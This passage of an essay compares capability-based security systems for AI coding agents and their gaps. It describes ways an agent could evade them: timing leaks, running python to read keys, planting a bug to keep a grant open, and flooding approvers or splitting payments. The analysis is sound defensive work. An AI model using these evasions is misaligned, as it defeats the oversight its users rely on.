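TACIT and LACUNA leave the agent's model out of the trusted base and allow for a model that cooperates fully with an attacker, but their security depends on a compiler with an experimental feature. Machine-checked proofs exist for the type system underneath capture checking, but Odersky and colleagues say that safe mode still needs one. Neither TACIT nor CaMeL prevents every covert channel. In TACIT, a function inside `map` could leak one bit by taking longer when the secret has a certain property.

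### A shell command that can do almost anything

Once a Scala program starts another program, the compiler can't control what that program does. Odersky and colleagues acknowledge this and recommend allowing only specific safe commands, with a sandbox around them. Yet an example in TACIT's documentation requests permission to run `pip` and `python`. With `python`, an agent could read the private key directly from the disk and send it anywhere, unless the sandbox prevents it.

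PORTICO tries to work out which files, servers and other resources a command will affect. If it can't, it refuses the command or asks a person. This works for a command that copies a file, but it is much harder for one that runs code. In the timeout example, the agent is allowed to edit and run the test for `api.py`. It could make the test open the packaging notes, and PORTICO would detect only a permitted test command.

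The agent also has some influence over when its grant ends. PORTICO runs the tests itself, but the agent writes the code they test. The agent could leave a mistake in `serialization.py` to keep the tests failing and the grant open until the phase ends.

Both systems therefore need operating-system isolation for any command that runs arbitrary code. For example, the test process can be given only the files the agent may currently use and no network access. Users also have to take away the agent's other tools. TACIT connects to existing coding agents as an additional tool, so an agent that keeps its ordinary shell can avoid the compiler.

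### A task whose needs nobody knows in advance

Suppose Priya asks an agent to find out why last night's sales report was wrong. The cause could be in the report's code, a settings file, the database or another team's service. To write a PORTICO contract, she would have to list the places the agent might need to look, and to do that well she would almost have to know the cause already. Miller raised the same objection to sandboxes with fixed lists.

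Requests during the task help only if the contract has a rule for them. Santos-Grueiro says some of PORTICO's failures happened because grants were too narrow or closed too early, or because the agent had no way to request something it needed. He would let a trusted event, such as a new approval, reopen a closed grant, and he prefers a task that visibly fails to one that succeeds with too much access.

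*Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, notes that agents are designed to look for another way after someone denies a request, so a refusal may not end the attempt. Several participants had also seen agents do more than they were asked while staying inside the folder they were allowed to use, which a grant limited to that folder would not prevent.

With TACIT, Priya wouldn't have to predict which private records the agent will read. She could wrap the whole sales database, and the agent could compute totals from any part of it without passing any rows to its model. Wrapping doesn't work for the report's code, because the model has to read the code to find a mistake in it. Wrapping also doesn't prevent the agent from changing or deleting the wrong file.

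Priya could instead grant access to each thing as the agent needs it, as with a powerbox. But an agent may need dozens of things in an hour, and she would have to judge every request.

### A person who approves every request

Researchers call the habit of approving prompts unread *approval fatigue*. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analysed 290 reports of problems with agents and files. Human review played a part in 105 of them. In 80 reports the user had switched on automatic approval, often to avoid hundreds of prompts in a session. In 31, the prompt did not contain enough information for the user. For example, a request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it permits whatever the script contains.

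Participants in *Let the Agent Do It?* also described clicking through familiar prompts, especially under time pressure, so repeated approvals are poor evidence that the user trusts the agent. According to *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026), current remedies either extend trust to more actions, as "always allow" does, or approve actions automatically inside a sandbox, which helps only if the sandbox is configured correctly.

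Attackers can exploit approvers' fatigue by sending many requests. In simulations for *Approve What, Exactly?* (2026), this flooding always succeeded when the number of requests was unlimited. With a limit, it succeeded about half the time in most tests. The approvers were programs, so the results are better evidence of the direction of the effect than of its size. The paper also tested an attack that needs no approval, in which the agent splits a large payment into small ones that the policy permits. This always worked until the policy also limited the total.

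A careless user does less harm in a system where some actions are impossible to approve. In TACIT, a program that would write Priya's key to the log doesn't compile, so she is never asked to approve it. PORTICO issues new grants only under rules in the contract, so an approval can reopen `serialization.py` but not the packaging notes. For commands it cannot analyse, PORTICO may rely on the user's answer, and a habit of clicking yes removes the protection in those cases.

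*Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) requires every action to have a capability, stay within the task's limits and have enough budget. Some actions also need a person's approval, which cannot replace a missing capability. Before the agent can send sensitive data to a recipient that needs special permission, a person must approve the exact message to that recipient, and the approval works only once. A user who approves everything can still release data this way, and Zhang counts that user as part of the trusted base.

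### A policy written by the model it limits

Writing a contract for each task takes work, and Santos-Grueiro did not measure how much. Eight templates covered a collection of 70 test tasks, but somebody still has to fill them in. PORTICO doesn't let the agent's model write the contract during a task, because anything the model writes counts only as a request. PORTICO also cannot check whether a contract is a good one. When Santos-Grueiro added the packaging notes to a contract as an experiment, PORTICO let the agent read them.

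TACIT is weaker here than its types suggest, because the agent's program chooses which folder to request, as in `requestFileSystem("/project")`. The compiler would also accept `requestFileSystem("/")`, which means the whole disk. The same is true of the lists of commands and servers. Whoever deploys TACIT has to build limits on these requests into its library. The wrapper still protects the folders marked as private, since the agent doesn't choose which folders those are.

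If the model writes the policy before it reads anything from outsiders, as CaMeL's planning model does with its program, prompt injection cannot influence the policy. But the model may still write a policy that requests too much authority, either through carelessness or, if it is working against its user, on purpose.

A model can safely write policies that only divide up access it already has. In LACUNA, code written by the model can call the model again for part of a task and choose what that call may use. The code can pass on a read-only file and withhold the network, but it cannot pass on a capability it never received. The first grant has to come from outside the model, normally from the person who starts the agent.
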